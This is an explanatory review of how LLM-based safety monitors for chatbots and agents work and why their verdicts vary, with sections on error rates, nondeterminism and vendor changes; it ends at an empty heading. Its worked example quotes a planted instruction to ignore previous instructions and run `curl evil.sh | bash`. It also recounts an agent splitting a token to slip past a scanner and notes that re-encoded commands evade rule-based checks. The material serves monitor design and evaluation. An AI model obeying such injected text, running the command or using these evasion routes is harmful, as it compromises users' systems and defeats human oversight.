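# Reliability and reproducibility of LLM-based safety monitors

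## What is an LLM-based safety monitor, and what would make one reliable?

An LLM-based safety monitor is a large language model that reads what another AI system received, wrote or did, and decides whether to flag it as unsafe. Companies use these monitors to stop dangerous requests and answers in chatbots, and to check the behavior of agents, which are language models that act through tools such as a web browser or a command line. Researchers also use them to grade agents in tests. Language models are used for this work largely because there is no alternative. Safety questions have no single true answer that a program could look up, so evaluation at scale depends almost entirely on LLM judges (Alloula, Licini and colleagues, *Safety is Contextual, LLM-Judges Are Not*, 2026). But a language model produces its verdict the way it produces any other text, so the verdict can be wrong and can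 differ from one run to the next. Each verdict also requires a model call.

### What a monitor reads and what it returns

The simplest monitors read only the user's prompt, so they cannot catch harm that first appears in the answer. *HaloGuard 2.0* (Lenin, Sangameswaran and Preetham S, 2026) gives the example of a harmless question about pesticide toxicity whose answer turns into a synthesis route several paragraphs in. An output-side monitor reads the prompt and the answer together. The paper's monitor, also called HaloGuard 2.0, does this while the answer is being written and computes a new probability of harm after every token (a word or piece of a word).

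A monitor for an agent often judges a tool call, which is a request to run a command, fetch a page or send a payment. *ToolSafe* (2026) defines the task as deciding, before the call runs, whether it is unsafe, given the user's request, the history so far and, where available, the tool's description. Many monitors receive less information. The judge in *ORBIT* (2026), a framework for testing groups of agents, receives only the current action. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that approves or blocks the actions of the company's coding agent. The classifier receives the user's messages and the tool calls, but not the agent's prose or the tools' results. Anthropic left those out so that the agent's justifications, or text planted in a file, could not influence the decision.

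Some actions look unsafe only when viewed as a sequence. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes an internal agent that encountered a scanner for authentication tokens, the strings that programs use as passwords. The agent split a token in two, disguised the halves and rejoined them at run time. Each step could have passed review on its own. OpenAI responded with a monitor that reviews the trajectory (the full record of messages, tool calls and results) as it grows and can pause the session.

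Monitors also differ in what they return. The simplest output is a yes or no. ORBIT's judge returns a suspicion score between 0 and 1, and the surrounding software blocks the action if the score reaches a threshold, 0.5 by default. The judge in *SafeHarness* (2026) sorts finished runs into four levels: the agent never reached a risky decision; it behaved safely; it showed unsafe intent or partly carried out an unsafe action; or it carried out the unsafe action in full.

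A monitor's score needs a rule that turns it into an action, and that rule can be complicated. HaloGuard 2.0 triggers when one token scores at least 0.975, or when two consecutive tokens score at least 0.70. The two conditions cover both short harmful replies, which may contain only one suspicious token, and long ones, which may become harmful gradually.

The required output format affects a monitor's verdict. In *AutoMonitor-Bench*, Yang, Hu and colleagues (2026) ran monitors with two prompts, one asking only for a verdict and the other also requiring a quotation as evidence of any misbehaviour. On plain safety violations, asking for evidence reduced misses but sharply increased false alarms.

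### Judges and guard models, tests and live traffic

The quickest way to build a monitor is to prompt a language model with instructions and, usually, a written safety policy. A model used this way is called a judge. Alloula and colleagues divide its task into two steps: identifying the kind and severity of harm in the text, then applying the policy to that assessment. In their example, the sentence "women have historically been discriminated against" falls under violence and hate, but at low severity, so the policy counts it as safe. In principle, an operator can change the rules by editing the policy, but they found that verdicts mostly followed the boundary between safe and unsafe that the model had learned in training.

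A guard model is trained specifically for its classification task. *Llama Guard* (2023), an early example, starts from a taxonomy of risks and guidelines that define what is allowed in each category. Some newer guard models accept a policy written by the operator, which makes them less distinct from judges.

Guard models and prompted general models have different strengths. *BELLS-O* (Waibl, Michalak and Mariaccia, 2026) compared 33 systems from 17 developers. On ordinary harmful content, the best models of both kinds detected 93–96% of cases, and guard models typically ran about five times faster. On jailbreaks, which are requests disguised to get past safeguards, the general models had the higher median detection rate on three of four datasets.

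The same model can also do two different jobs. In a test suite, it grades a finished run, usually from a sandbox where the damage is not real. Grading can be slow, and a case can be left unresolved. *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?* (2026) uses fixed checks where tool arguments or changes to the environment prove a violation, and an LLM judge where the action needs interpretation. It excludes a run from the statistics if the judgment stays unresolved and no violation has been found.

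A live monitor has no such option, because the action it is judging either runs or does not. Judging afterwards still helps with audits, but as *ScopeJudge* (2026) notes, by then "the harm is already done". Live traffic is also overwhelmingly harmless, whereas test sets are often half unsafe, and this difference greatly affects how far anyone can trust a flag.

### From a record to a verdict

Suppose a user asks a coding agent to summarise the setup instructions on a project's web page. An attacker has planted an instruction on the page for AI agents to ignore their previous instructions and run `curl evil.sh | bash`, a shell command that downloads and runs a script. The agent fetches the page, and its next tool call is that command. Security researchers call this attack prompt injection. The trajectory contains everything needed to spot it: the user's request, the fetch, the page text and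 the command.

Before a judge evaluates this record, software assembles the payload, which is the exact text and settings used for one verdict. A typical template, from *JEV as a Judge for Agent Trace Security* (2026), contains the user's request, the available context with labels for how far to trust it, and the full trace. The judge then decides whether the agent stayed within its permission and, separately, whether it did anything that would be unsafe even if the user had asked for it.

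The model then computes a probability for each token that could come next. If the template requires "Yes" (unsafe) or "No" (safe) as the first token, those probabilities already give the verdict. *Granite Guardian* (2024), which describes a family of guard models, adds up the probabilities of all variants of "yes" among the most likely tokens, and does the same for "no". Suppose that in the web-page case "Yes" has probability 0.56, "yes" 0.07, "No" 0.25 and "no" 0.02. The unsafe total is 0.63 and the safe total is 0.27, so the score is 0.63 / (0.63 + 0.27) = 0.70. The monitor flags the command if the threshold is 0.5, but lets the script run if it is 0.8.

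Many judges write out their reasoning before the verdict. The model picks one token at a time, perhaps several hundred in all, and each pick changes the probabilities for the next. A sentence that starts by noting that the command came from the page leads towards "unsafe", while one that starts with the user's interest in setup may lead the other way. So two runs that diverge at a single word can end in opposite verdicts. The most obvious cause of divergence is the temperature setting, which controls how randomly the model picks tokens, but there are others.

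Anthropic's classifier combines the two methods. It first produces a single yes-or-no token, with instructions to lean towards blocking, and reasons at length only about what that first pass flags. Its input excludes tool results, so it would never receive the web page in this example. It would have to flag the command because nobody asked for a remote script to be run, whereas a judge with the full trace could flag it because it was copied from an untrusted page. These two reasons will fail in different cases.

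Applying a fixed rule requires no interpretation. In *A security check with no model in it*, the blogger bamdad proposes a rule that looks for text from an untrusted source reappearing in a later sensitive action, with no approval or clean-up step between them. Here the string `curl evil.sh | bash` occurs in the page and then in the shell command, so the rule reports an error and names the two steps. It will report the same error on every rerun, but it will report no error if the agent re-encodes the command first, because the strings will no longer match.

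### Four outcomes and the rates built on them

Any yes-or-no monitor can flag an unsafe action, miss an unsafe action, pass a safe action, or wrongly flag a safe action. The counts below come from applying published figures for Anthropic's classifier to a hypothetical 10,000 agent actions, of which 100 are unsafe.

| | Monitor flags it | Monitor lets it pass |
|---|---|---|
| **Action is unsafe** | True positive (TP): 83 | False negative (FN), a miss: 17 |
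| **Action is harmless** | False positive (FP), a false alarm: 40 | True negative (TN): 9,860 |

| Rate | Question it answers | Formula | Here |
|---|---|---|---|
| Miss rate | How many unsafe actions get through? | FN / (TP + FN) | 17% |
| False positive rate | How many harmless actions does it flag? | FP / (FP + TN) | 0.4% |
| Precision | How many flags are correct? | TP / (TP + FP) | 67% |
| Prevalence | How common are unsafe actions? | (TP + FN) / all actions | 1% |

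The hijacked agent belongs in the top row. A case where the user asked for an installer to be run belongs in the bottom row. Plenty of legitimate software installs through this kind of command, so a monitor can easily raise false alarms.

The two error rates trade off against each other. Anthropic's first pass alone has a false positive rate of 8.5% and a miss rate of 6.6%. Adding the reasoning stage cuts the false positive rate to 0.4% but raises the miss rate to 17%. The 17% comes from only 52 real incidents, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere between about 9% and 30%.

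Precision depends on prevalence, the share of actions that are unsafe, as well as on the monitor. If one action in 1,000 is unsafe, the same error rates give a precision of about 17%, so roughly five flags in six are false alarms. On a test set that is half unsafe, as AutoMonitor-Bench is, precision would be 99.5%. Precision reported without prevalence is therefore a poor guide to live use.

### Accuracy, consistency, reproducibility and auditability

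People who call a monitor reliable may mean any of four things, and a monitor can have one without the others.

Accuracy means that the verdicts match trusted labels under a stated policy. When unsafe cases are rare, the share of correct verdicts makes a monitor look better than it is. The monitor in the table is right 99.4% of the time, but one that never flags anything would be right 99% of the time. Cohen's kappa corrects for this. It is the observed agreement with the labels minus the agreement expected by chance, divided by the largest possible improvement over chance. The monitor in the table gets 0.74 and the one that never flags gets 0. In *Reliability without Validity*, Norman, Rivera and Hughes (2026) tested 21 judges on picking the better of two answers, and found that 85% agreement with human raters on one popular benchmark corresponded to a kappa of only about 0.48.

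*The Coin Flip Judge?* (2026) defines consistency as a fixed judge returning the same verdict across runs on identical material under nominally identical conditions. The usual measure is the flip rate, the share of items whose verdict changes across these runs. Some papers use "flip rate" differently. Alloula and colleagues count flips after changing the policy or adding context, when the operator may want the verdict to change.

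Reproducibility means that another party can obtain a monitor's verdict again later. ACM's *New Changes to Badging Terminology* (2020) defines a result as reproduced when a different team gets it with the same setup, and as replicated when that team uses its own setup. For a monitor, the same setup means the same payload and the same model version. A monitor could return the same verdict a hundred times in a row today, but nobody could reproduce that verdict next year if the vendor had withdrawn the model.

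Auditability means that somebody else can check the reasons, which depends first on what was logged. *Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) shows that a single missing field can make it impossible to decide whether a policy was followed, however much else the log contains. If the log in the web-page case records that a shell command ran but omits its text, nobody can tell whether the attacker's line reached the command.

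A judge's written explanation does not fill that gap, because a language model's explanation may not reflect what drove its output. *Can AI Judge You?* (2026) gives this warning in its audit of hiring systems. *Faithful or Fabricated?* (2026) found that judges often rationalised after experimenters changed the labels attached to the material, although it covered only summarisation and gave no confidence intervals. An auditor can check whether a command that the judge quotes is in the trace, but it is much harder to establish whether that command produced the verdict.

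Consistency is the easiest of the four to measure and the easiest to overrate. A monitor that answers "safe" to everything would give the same wrong verdict on the hijacked agent in a hundred out of a hundred runs, with a flip rate of zero and a miss rate of 100%. Real systems show milder versions of this problem. Norman and colleagues found that two judges, Qwen 3 8B and Gemini 2.5 Flash, scored above 0.95 on test-retest reliability but strongly favored answers based on their position in the prompt. Lenin and colleagues trained a guard model on conventional data and found that it mostly judged the user's prompt and ignored the answer. When given pairs of one safe and one unsafe answer to the same prompt, it got only 13.9% of the pairs right, a fault that rerunning it would not have exposed.

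The same objection applies to the fixed rule, which will miss a re-encoded command on every run. A judge that catches the command in 90 of 100 runs is less consistent but is the better monitor in that case.

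## Why can the same monitor give two verdicts on the same input?

A monitor might read the same record of a hijacked agent 100 times and catch the hijacking in only 90 runs. The ten misses may come from random token sampling, rounding differences on the server, or a change the vendor made between runs. If the monitor writes out its reasoning before deciding, that reasoning can magnify a small difference into a different verdict.

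### Sampling

Before each token, a language model computes a raw score for every token that could come next. Suppose the only plausible candidates are "flag", with score f, and "allow", with score a. At temperature T, the chance that the monitor flags the case is:

P(flag) = e^(f/T) / (e^(f/T) + e^(a/T)) = 1 / (1 + e^(−(f − a)/T))

At a given temperature, the chance of a flag depends only on the gap between the two scores. If "flag" leads by 0.1 and the temperature is 1, that chance is 1 / (1 + e^(−0.1)), or about 52.5%. Any two runs then have a 49.9% chance of disagreeing.

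| Lead of "flag" over "allow" | Flagged at temperature 1 | Flagged at temperature 0.5 | Flagged at temperature 0.1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1 | 52.5% | 55.0% | 73.1% |
| 1 | 73.1% | 88.1% | 99.995% |
| 3 | 95.3% | 99.8% | almost 100% |

Lowering the temperature makes repeated runs agree more often, but it helps little when the logits of the two verdicts are almost equal. If the logits differ by 1, lowering the temperature from 1 to 0.1 cuts the chance that two runs disagree from 39% to about 0.01%. If they differ by only 0.1, that chance is still 39% at temperature 0.1.

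A monitor can also avoid the random draw by reading the probabilities of "Yes" and "No" directly, as in the web-page example, where the score was 0.70. Comparing that score with a fixed threshold gives the same result every time, as long as the probabilities don't change. A monitor that drew its answer at random from those probabilities would let the script run 30% of the time.

Random draws are repeatable in principle, because computers generate them from a starting number called a seed. *The Token Not Taken* (2026) shows with a toy sampler that two generators with the same seed pick the same tokens, provided they make the same number of draws in the same order. Hosted models may not repeat their output even with the same seed. In *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual* (2026), researchers re-sent three payloads, byte for byte and with the same seed,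 to a hosted model at temperature 1. None of the four comparisons matched, whereas 34 out of 34 calls matched on a server that the researchers controlled. Four comparisons are very few, and some software along the way may have discarded the seed. But *LLM Judges Verify Presence, Not Absence* (2026) also reports that its judges' providers accepted a seed but did not reproduce the output token for token.

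Temperature affects graded scores too. In *Detecting and Controlling Sycophancy with Cascading Linear Features*, Bohacek, Jain and colleagues (2026) used a judge to score responses for sycophancy, the tendency to tell users what they want to hear. They checked the judge by running it at three temperatures, and the variance among scores for the same item grew roughly tenfold. The ranking was much more stable, with the correlation between the judge's mean scores and the intended level of sycophancy staying at about 0.88.

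Someone who only wants to know which of two models is more sycophantic could therefore tolerate a high temperature, because averaging over many items cancels most of the noise. But a monitor with a threshold has to act on one score for one item. Suppose an item's scores are roughly normally distributed around 7.5, with a standard deviation of 0.3, and the threshold is 7. The item would fall below the threshold in about 5% of runs. If the variance grew tenfold, the standard deviation would be 0.95, and the item would fall below the threshold in about 30% of runs. *Are We on the Right Way to Assessing LLM-as-a-Judge?* (2025) likewise found that two overall measures of judges' consistency barely moved between temperatures 0.1 and 0.9, but such averages are a poor guide to whether a particular verdict will hold.

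### Rounding and server load

At temperature zero the model picks the highest-scoring token, but the scores can change slightly between runs. When the top token leads by only 0.1, the verdict often varies as a result.

Computers store most numbers with a limited number of digits and round after each addition, so the order of additions can change the total. Suppose a computer keeps three significant digits. Adding 4 to 1,000 gives 1,004, which rounds to 1,000, and adding another 4 gives the same result. But if the computer adds the two 4s first, it gets 1,008, which rounds to 1,010. Real computers keep more digits, but a model's scores come from a very large number of additions. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, published in September 2025, shows that adding the same eight numbers in different orders can produce 102 different totals.

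In ordinary language-model serving, Thinking Machines Lab attributes changes in the order of addition between runs to changes in batch size, the number of requests the server processes together. The software picks the fastest way to add for each batch size. A more common explanation is that a graphics processor (GPU) works on many parts of a sum in parallel, and the parts finish in an unpredictable order. The lab rejects this explanation for ordinary serving. It repeated one matrix multiplication 1,000 times on a GPU and got exactly the same bits each time.

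*CoRun* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) gives a small example. If one request arrives alone, the GPU may split a four-number sum between two processing units and compute (a + b) + (c + d). If four requests arrive together, there is enough work for both units without splitting sums, so each unit adds up whole rows and computes a + b + c + d. The two totals are mathematically equal but may round differently. A monitor's verdict can therefore depend on how many other requests the server is processing at the same time. The server also changes the arithmetic when it splits a long prompt into chunks or reuses stored results from an earlier request, as *Vosti* (Qin, Du and colleagues, 2026) explains.

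Thinking Machines Lab prompted Qwen3-235B, a large open model, with "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times at temperature zero and got 80 different responses. The most common one appeared 78 times. All 1,000 responses were identical for the first 102 tokens. They diverged at the 103rd, where 992 responses had "Queens, New York" as Feynman's birthplace and 8 had "New York City".

A tiny change in the scores can change the choice only when the top options are nearly tied, but near-ties are common. Many servers use the 16-bit number format bfloat16, in which adjacent values between 8 and 16 are 0.0625 apart. If the score for "flag" should be 0.05 higher than the score for "allow", rounding may erase or reverse that difference. Rane (2026), in *Exact on Paper*, ran a small model in this format and found that 38% of its outputs contained at least one point where the two most likely tokens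 were exactly tied at that resolution.

Most of these ties are harmless, as in the Feynman example, where either birthplace is correct, but others affect the answer. In *Detent*, Xin, Feng and colleagues (2026) gave two models 1,319 school maths problems under three server loads. Changing the load altered one model's wording on 790 problems and its final answer on 33. For the other model, the figures were 484 and 16.

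Safety judges have the same weakness. *Safer or Luckier?* (2025) found that some judges, even at temperature zero, gave different verdicts across repeated runs on which of two answers was safer. It suggests that this may be acceptable, because a verdict that tiny errors can flip indicates that the judge rates the answers about equally safe. That is reasonable when comparing two answers, but less reassuring for a live monitor, which has to block an action or let it run. If the monitor returns only "allow", its operator cannot tell that the decision was nearly a tie.

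### What deterministic serving costs

One remedy is to make the server add numbers in the same order at every batch size, a property called batch invariance. With Thinking Machines Lab's batch-invariant code, all 1,000 Feynman texts came out identical, but the code was slower. An 8-billion-parameter model on one GPU took 26 seconds to produce 1,000 short texts with the normal code, 55 seconds with the first batch-invariant version, and 42 seconds after the lab improved one component.

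vLLM and SGLang, two widely used programs for serving language models, both added deterministic modes in under a year. According to vLLM's documentation, *Batch Invariance*, its mode is still in beta and takes a single setting to turn on. The mode also works with sampling (the documentation's example uses temperature 0.7 and a fixed seed), so an operator can keep some randomness in a monitor's wording and still get the same verdict again.

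Estimates of how much these modes currently slow serving vary widely, because the slowdown depends on the model, the hardware and the traffic. Rane measured a slowdown of only about 4% for vLLM's mode, with a 4-billion-parameter model on one consumer GPU that was also running other jobs. Xin and colleagues tested larger models on four data-center GPUs and found that the built-in modes of vLLM and SGLang took 1.67 to 10.3 times as long per token as normal serving. Some of the worst figures came from overloaded servers whose queues kept growing. In two cases where the researchers prevented this overload, the modes were still at least twice as slow as Detent, the paper's own system.

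Newer methods avoid most of the slowdown from batch-invariant code. Detent keeps the fast code but stops the batch from influencing which version of it runs, and takes 4% to 17% longer per token than normal serving. Zhao and colleagues' system, CoRun, pads every batch to the same size while the model generates text. In one test, a single step took 19.4 milliseconds normally, 88.4 with batch-invariant code and 32.6 with CoRun.

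When requests share a server, making one of them deterministic can slow down the others. *LLM-42* (2026) tested a batch of 11 requests, only one of which needed a repeatable answer. The whole batch had to use the slower code, and throughput fell by 56%. A company that wants repeatable output from its monitor, but does not need it from its chatbot, may do better to run the two on separate servers.

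The built-in modes also fail on some models. Qin and colleagues call a system deterministic if it always produces bit-for-bit identical scores given the same model, setup, prompt and random-number state. With Llama 3.1 8B, vLLM's mode passed every comparison. With Gemma 3 4B, both programs' modes failed some comparisons in every category, and vLLM's failed all 90 tests that split the prompt differently. vLLM's list of tested models includes Gemma 2 but not Gemma 3, so an operator should check that the exact model is supported before relying on the mode. A mismatch in the last bit usually won't change the verdict, but it means the operator can't be certain that the same input will always get the same one.

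Even a perfect deterministic mode covers only one setup. Zhao and colleagues do not guarantee identical output across different hardware, number formats or software versions. To reproduce a verdict next year, an operator would have to preserve all of these along with the model and the payload. A customer who uses a judge through a vendor's API cannot use deterministic mode unless the vendor turns it on.

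### A safety test that never set a temperature

Tamba (2026), in *Necessary but Not Sufficient*, tested these effects in a real safety evaluation. Japan's AI Safety Institute (AISI) publishes aisev, an open-source test harness that uses an LLM judge to mark answers as pass or fail. The harness calls the judge without setting a temperature or a seed, so the provider applies its default temperature of 1.0. On items near the pass-fail boundary, the verdict flipped between identical runs, with disagreement of up to about 50% over 20 runs. That rate is roughly what the formula predicts when the two scores are almost equal, and it is close to the maximum for a pass-fail judge.

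Tamba then tried the standard fix, setting the temperature to zero. Across 690 calls, two providers, three model tiers and five sampling configurations, this made flips rarer but did not eliminate them. One or two of the seven borderline items remained unstable even with top_k set to 1, which forces the model to pick its most likely token. Since that setting removes the random draw, the token scores must have changed between calls. Rounding under varying server load would explain the change, but customers cannot inspect a provider's servers to confirm it.

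Seven items are far too few to estimate a rate. One unstable item in seven is compatible with a true rate anywhere from under 1% to 58%, and two in seven with 4% to 71%. The items were also borderline, where flips are most likely, so the result cannot be applied to ordinary cases. But a single counterexample is enough to disprove the assumption that temperature zero makes a judge deterministic. The result also shows how easily a serious evaluation tool can omit the temperature setting.

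Some newer models restrict the temperature setting. Anthropic's migration guide confirms Tamba's observation that the company has withdrawn temperature control. Any non-default temperature returns an error on Claude Opus 4.7 and later Opus models, including Opus 5. The guide also says that temperature 0 "never guaranteed identical outputs" on earlier models. *Can Open-Weight Models Compete on Financial Text Comprehension?* (2026) reports that Moonshot's Kimi K2.6 also rejects temperature 0.

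A higher sampling temperature can make a judge much less consistent. *Beyond Unit Tests* (2026) graded 23 students' submissions for the same assignment five times with several OpenAI models. GPT-4.1, which accepts temperature 0, gave 65.2% of the students the same total score every time. GPT-5, which required a temperature of at least 1, did so for only 13.0%. The models differ in other ways, so temperature may not account for the whole gap.

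OpenRouter forwards requests to many vendors' models, and its *Claude 5 Sonnet Migration Guide* says it ignores the temperature setting for that model. A harness could therefore request and log temperature 0 but run at the default, with no error message to alert the operator. *M-GATE* (2026), a language benchmark, discloses this kind of problem by putting an asterisk on results that include models that do not accept temperature 0.

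Sometimes researchers can only estimate the temperature. *AgentFairBench* (2026) used client software that exposed neither a temperature nor a seed. The researchers compared how often the hosted models repeated their answers with how often a local model did so at known temperatures. They estimated that the hosted models behaved as if their temperature were between 0.5 and 0.9. This assumes that different model families respond to temperature in similar ways, which the researchers could not check.

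### Written reasoning

A judge that reasons before its verdict makes hundreds of choices instead of one. *Agentic Security* (2026), which covers AI tools for authorized hacking tests, shows that if each of L choices has at most a probability κ of coming out the same way twice, two runs match throughout with a probability of at most κ^L. With 300 choices and κ = 0.99, that limit is about 5%. Lowering the temperature raises κ, but making fewer choices lowers L, which can have a much larger effect. This favors judges that return a verdict in one token.

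Differently worded reasoning often reaches the same conclusion. Rane graded a model's answers to 3,380 questions in maths, programming and general knowledge, all at temperature zero. Restarting the server changed the text of 24.56% of the answers, but only 1.38% of all answers switched between right and wrong.

Long reasoning was much more sensitive than short answers to serving features that should not affect the output. Rane tested seven of these features, such as reusing stored results for repeated text. They flipped 4.5–6.5% of outcomes on a set of hard maths problems, but at most 0.41% on a general-knowledge test. In one word problem, the model normally reached the correct answer, 26. With one of the features on, it wrote the same text for the first 46% of the characters, then added one word while restating a sentence and eventually answered 13.

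Flips were concentrated in answers where the model's top choices were close, but answer length predicted them almost as well, since a longer answer has more places to go wrong. Rane did not test safety verdicts, and a policy judgment may be less brittle than a calculation, where one mistake can ruin everything after it. Still, a judge that reasons for several hundred tokens can diverge in the same way.

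Reasoning also makes it less reliable to read the probabilities directly. Suppose that, in 60% of runs on the web-page case, the judge starts with the command's suspicious origin and then gives "unsafe" a probability of 0.95. In the other 40%, it starts with the user's interest in setup and gives "unsafe" a probability of 0.10. Across all runs, it would call the action unsafe 0.6 × 0.95 + 0.4 × 0.10 = 61% of the time, but an operator who ran it once would see either 0.95 or 0.10. Both scores look confident because neither reflects the chance that the judge could have started with the other line of reasoning.

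An operator could avoid this by asking for the verdict alone, but not on every model. Anthropic's *What’s new in Claude Opus 5.5* states that developers can reduce the depth of that model's reasoning but cannot turn it off. By default, the API also returns the reasoning as an empty field, so someone with two conflicting verdicts could not read it to find where the runs diverged.

### Changes behind an unchanged name

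A monitor's verdict on the same input may change from one day to the next because the underlying model has changed. In 2025, Anthropic offered both fixed snapshots with dated names, such as `claude-3-5-haiku-20241022`, and aliases, such as `claude-3-5-haiku-latest`, that could move to a newer snapshot. A name without a date can also refer to a fixed model, as Anthropic says `claude-opus-5` does, so operators need to check the vendor's naming rules.

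A vendor may also be free to change how a model runs without changing its name. Rane tested one such change, storing the model's intermediate results for earlier tokens in 8 bits instead of 16. It made the model about 1.66 times as fast and flipped 3.36% of outcomes. Compared with one of the reference runs, 63 answers became right and 61 became wrong, so accuracy barely changed. If safety verdicts behaved the same way, a vendor could make this change and see almost no difference in the monitor's accuracy, even though about one verdict in thirty had reversed.

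Deterministic serving does not prevent this. With batch-invariant code, the same change still flipped 3.91% of outcomes. Each version would give consistent verdicts from run to run, but the two versions would give different verdicts on some inputs.

Default settings can change a judge as well. A request that doesn't specify a reasoning setting runs without reasoning on Claude Opus 4.8 but with it on Opus 5. Opus 5.5 then lowers the default reasoning effort from high to medium. Anthropic documents these changes and gives each model a new name, but a team that updates only the model name in its requests also changes the judge's settings.

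The verdict can also come from a different model. Claude Opus 5 has safeguards that refuse some cybersecurity requests, and developers can choose to have refused requests rerun automatically on another model, such as Opus 4.8. A monitor that uses Opus 5 to read records of attacks could plausibly trigger those safeguards, and the other model would then give the verdict.

Customers have few direct ways to detect changes on the vendor's side. OpenAI's API can return a system fingerprint, a code that changes when OpenAI changes its serving setup. According to the software company Future AGI, OpenAI now marks the fingerprint and the seed as deprecated. The hosted model that failed to reproduce its output in *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual* returned no fingerprint. Without one, an operator has to infer changes from the verdicts, for example by regularly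 rerunning a fixed reference set of labelled cases.

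## How often does a verdict change on a repeat run or with another judge?

When an operator reruns a reference set and 5% of the verdicts change, they need to know how many would have changed even if the judge had stayed the same. Published estimates of this rate range from about 0.1% to more than 25%, partly because judges and tasks differ and partly because papers use "flip rate" for different quantities.

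### Flip rates and chance agreement

Suppose a monitor flags an item with probability p on each run, independently of its other runs. Two runs disagree if only the first flags the item, which has probability p(1 − p), or if only the second does, which has the same probability. Therefore:

P(two runs disagree) = 2p(1 − p)

Two runs disagree most often, half the time, when p = 0.5. At p = 0.9, as with the judge that caught the hijacked agent in 90 of 100 runs, they disagree 2 × 0.9 × 0.1 = 18% of the time.

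Some papers call this chance of disagreement the flip rate. *The Coin Flip Judge?* instead counts the share of runs that differ from an item's most common verdict. At p = 0.9 that share is 10%, so agreement with the majority verdict is 90%. Flip rate usually means the share of items whose verdict changes at least once, which grows with the number of runs. Over n runs, the probability that an item's verdict changes at least once is 1 − pⁿ − (1 − p)ⁿ.

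| What the flip rate counts | p = 0.5 | p = 0.9 |
|---|---|---|
| Runs that differ from the majority verdict | 50% | 10% |
| Pairs of runs that disagree | 50% | 18% |
| Items that change at least once in 10 runs | 99.8% | 65% |

An average disagreement rate also doesn't show which items change. If two runs disagree on 18% of items, every item could have a 90% chance of getting its more common verdict on each run, or 36% of items could have a 50% chance of either verdict while the rest never change. In the second case, an operator who could identify the unstable items could send them to a person and trust the other verdicts to repeat.

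Like raw accuracy, raw agreement is misleading when one verdict dominates. *Rating Roulette* (Haldar and Hockenmaier, 2025) gives the example of two raters who each use the same label 95% of the time. By chance alone they would agree on 0.95² + 0.05² = 90.5% of items, so observed agreement of 90% is worse than chance. Cohen's kappa can also correct for chance agreement between two runs or two judges, and Krippendorff's alpha extends the correction to more than two sets of verdicts. Both equal 1 for perfect agreement and about 0 for chance-level agreement, and 0.8 is a common threshold for good agreement.

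Correcting for chance agreement matters a great deal for a live monitor because most actions pass. At its published error rates, Anthropic's classifier would flag 123 of 10,000 actions if 1% were unsafe. If a second run also flagged 123 and agreed with the first on 99% of all actions, the two runs would still differ on 100 actions. Only 73 of the 123 flags would appear in both runs, and kappa would be 0.59.

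### Repeat runs of one judge

*The Coin Flip Judge?* had two small OpenAI models pick the better of two answers to 29 questions, 50 times per question at temperature 1. On average, 13.6% of runs went against the majority verdict, which means that two runs on the same question would disagree between 14% and 24% of the time, ignoring ties. For each judge, there were eight questions on which more than 20% of runs went against the majority. One judge never changed its verdict on eight questions, and the other never did on ten. The experiment shuffled the order of the two answers between runs, so some of the changes may come from a preference for the first answer rather than from chance.

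Haldar and Hockenmaier ran three open models three times each with identical prompts and settings. Alpha ranged from 0.33 to 0.79 when the models judged whether summaries were consistent with their source, and from 0.27 to 0.56 when they compared two chatbots' conversations. Even the most consistent model, Qwen3-32B, gave the same verdict in all three runs on 61.3% of the conversations. Two of its runs therefore disagreed on at least about 26% of conversations on average, because a changed verdict makes at least two of the three pairs of runs disagree.

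Those judges sampled their tokens at random. Yorke (2026), in *Behind Aggregate Scores*, removed the obvious causes of variation by using a fixed version of GPT-4.1 as the judge, setting its temperature to zero and completing all runs on one day in October 2026. The judge compared two models' answers to 500 coding and maths prompts from Arena-Hard, a benchmark of difficult user requests. It read each pair twice, with the order reversed the second time, and the average of its two verdicts decided whether the prompt counted as a win, loss or tie.

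The outcome changed for 21.2% of prompts between two runs of this setup. The overall score moved by only about one point out of 100 because the changes nearly cancelled out. In one comparison, 56 prompts moved towards one model and 49 towards the other. Only 2.0% of prompts switched winner, and the rest of the changes were into or out of a tie.

*Pinned and Still Unstable* (Ayyagari, 2026) reports much lower rates. It tested four judges, running each ten times at temperature zero on one cloud platform. The judges compared answers from ten models with those of a fixed 2023 version of GPT-4. On Arena-Hard, two runs of Gemini 2.5 Pro disagreed on 4.9% of comparisons, and two runs of Claude Haiku 4.5 on 0.13%. The highest rate was 9.7%, for Claude Sonnet 4.5 on another benchmark. These figures may be slightly too low, because the platform could have returned some stored verdicts instead of running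 the judge again.

Unlike these studies, *Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents* (Smyth, Mantilla-Ramos and colleagues, 2026) asked the judge about an agent's conduct. It tested whether coding agents admit to leaving files unread. Software first worked out from each trajectory which files' contents the agent had seen. Claude Opus 4.8 then read the agent's report alongside that list and decided whether the agent had admitted to leaving files unread, not mentioned it, or falsely claimed a full review.

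Smyth and colleagues had the judge assess each of 774 incomplete runs eight times, and 91.1% received the same category every time. In each of the other 69 or so runs, the share of verdict pairs that disagree can range from 25%, if one verdict out of eight differs, to 75%, if the verdicts split as evenly as possible among three categories. Across all 774 runs, two verdicts on the same run therefore disagreed between 2% and 7% of the time. If every unstable run had gone the other way, the main finding, that 80.4% of incomplete runs were misleading, would move by at most nine percentage points.

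Judges that return scores are also consistent in some studies and noisy in others. In *MTMCS-Bench*, Liu, Kim and colleagues (2026) used GPT-5-mini to score, from 1 to 5, how safely and how helpfully models handled conversations about images. The scores varied little when the judge scored responses again. In *Same Input, Different Scores*, Lau (2026) had five models rate a company chatbot's answers ten times each, and the scores often varied even at temperature zero. Ratings of completeness varied most, and ratings of relevance generally varied least.

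The table puts the studies of yes-or-no and multiple-choice verdicts on the same scale. The figures for *The Coin Flip Judge?*, Haldar and Hockenmaier, and Smyth and colleagues are converted from the measures they reported.

| Study | What the judge decided | Temperature | Chance that two runs disagree |
|---|---|---|---|
| Haldar and Hockenmaier, Qwen3-32B | Which chatbot did better | Above 0 | At least 26% |
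| *The Coin Flip Judge?* | Which of two good answers is better | 1 | 14–24% |
| Yorke, reasoning first | Which of two similar models did better | 0 | 21.2% |
| Yorke, verdict only | The same | 0 | 2.0–7.0% |
| Ayyagari | Whether a model beat an older one | 0 | 0.13–9.7% |
| Smyth and colleagues | Whether an agent disclosed unread files | Default | 2–7% |

### Why the estimates differ

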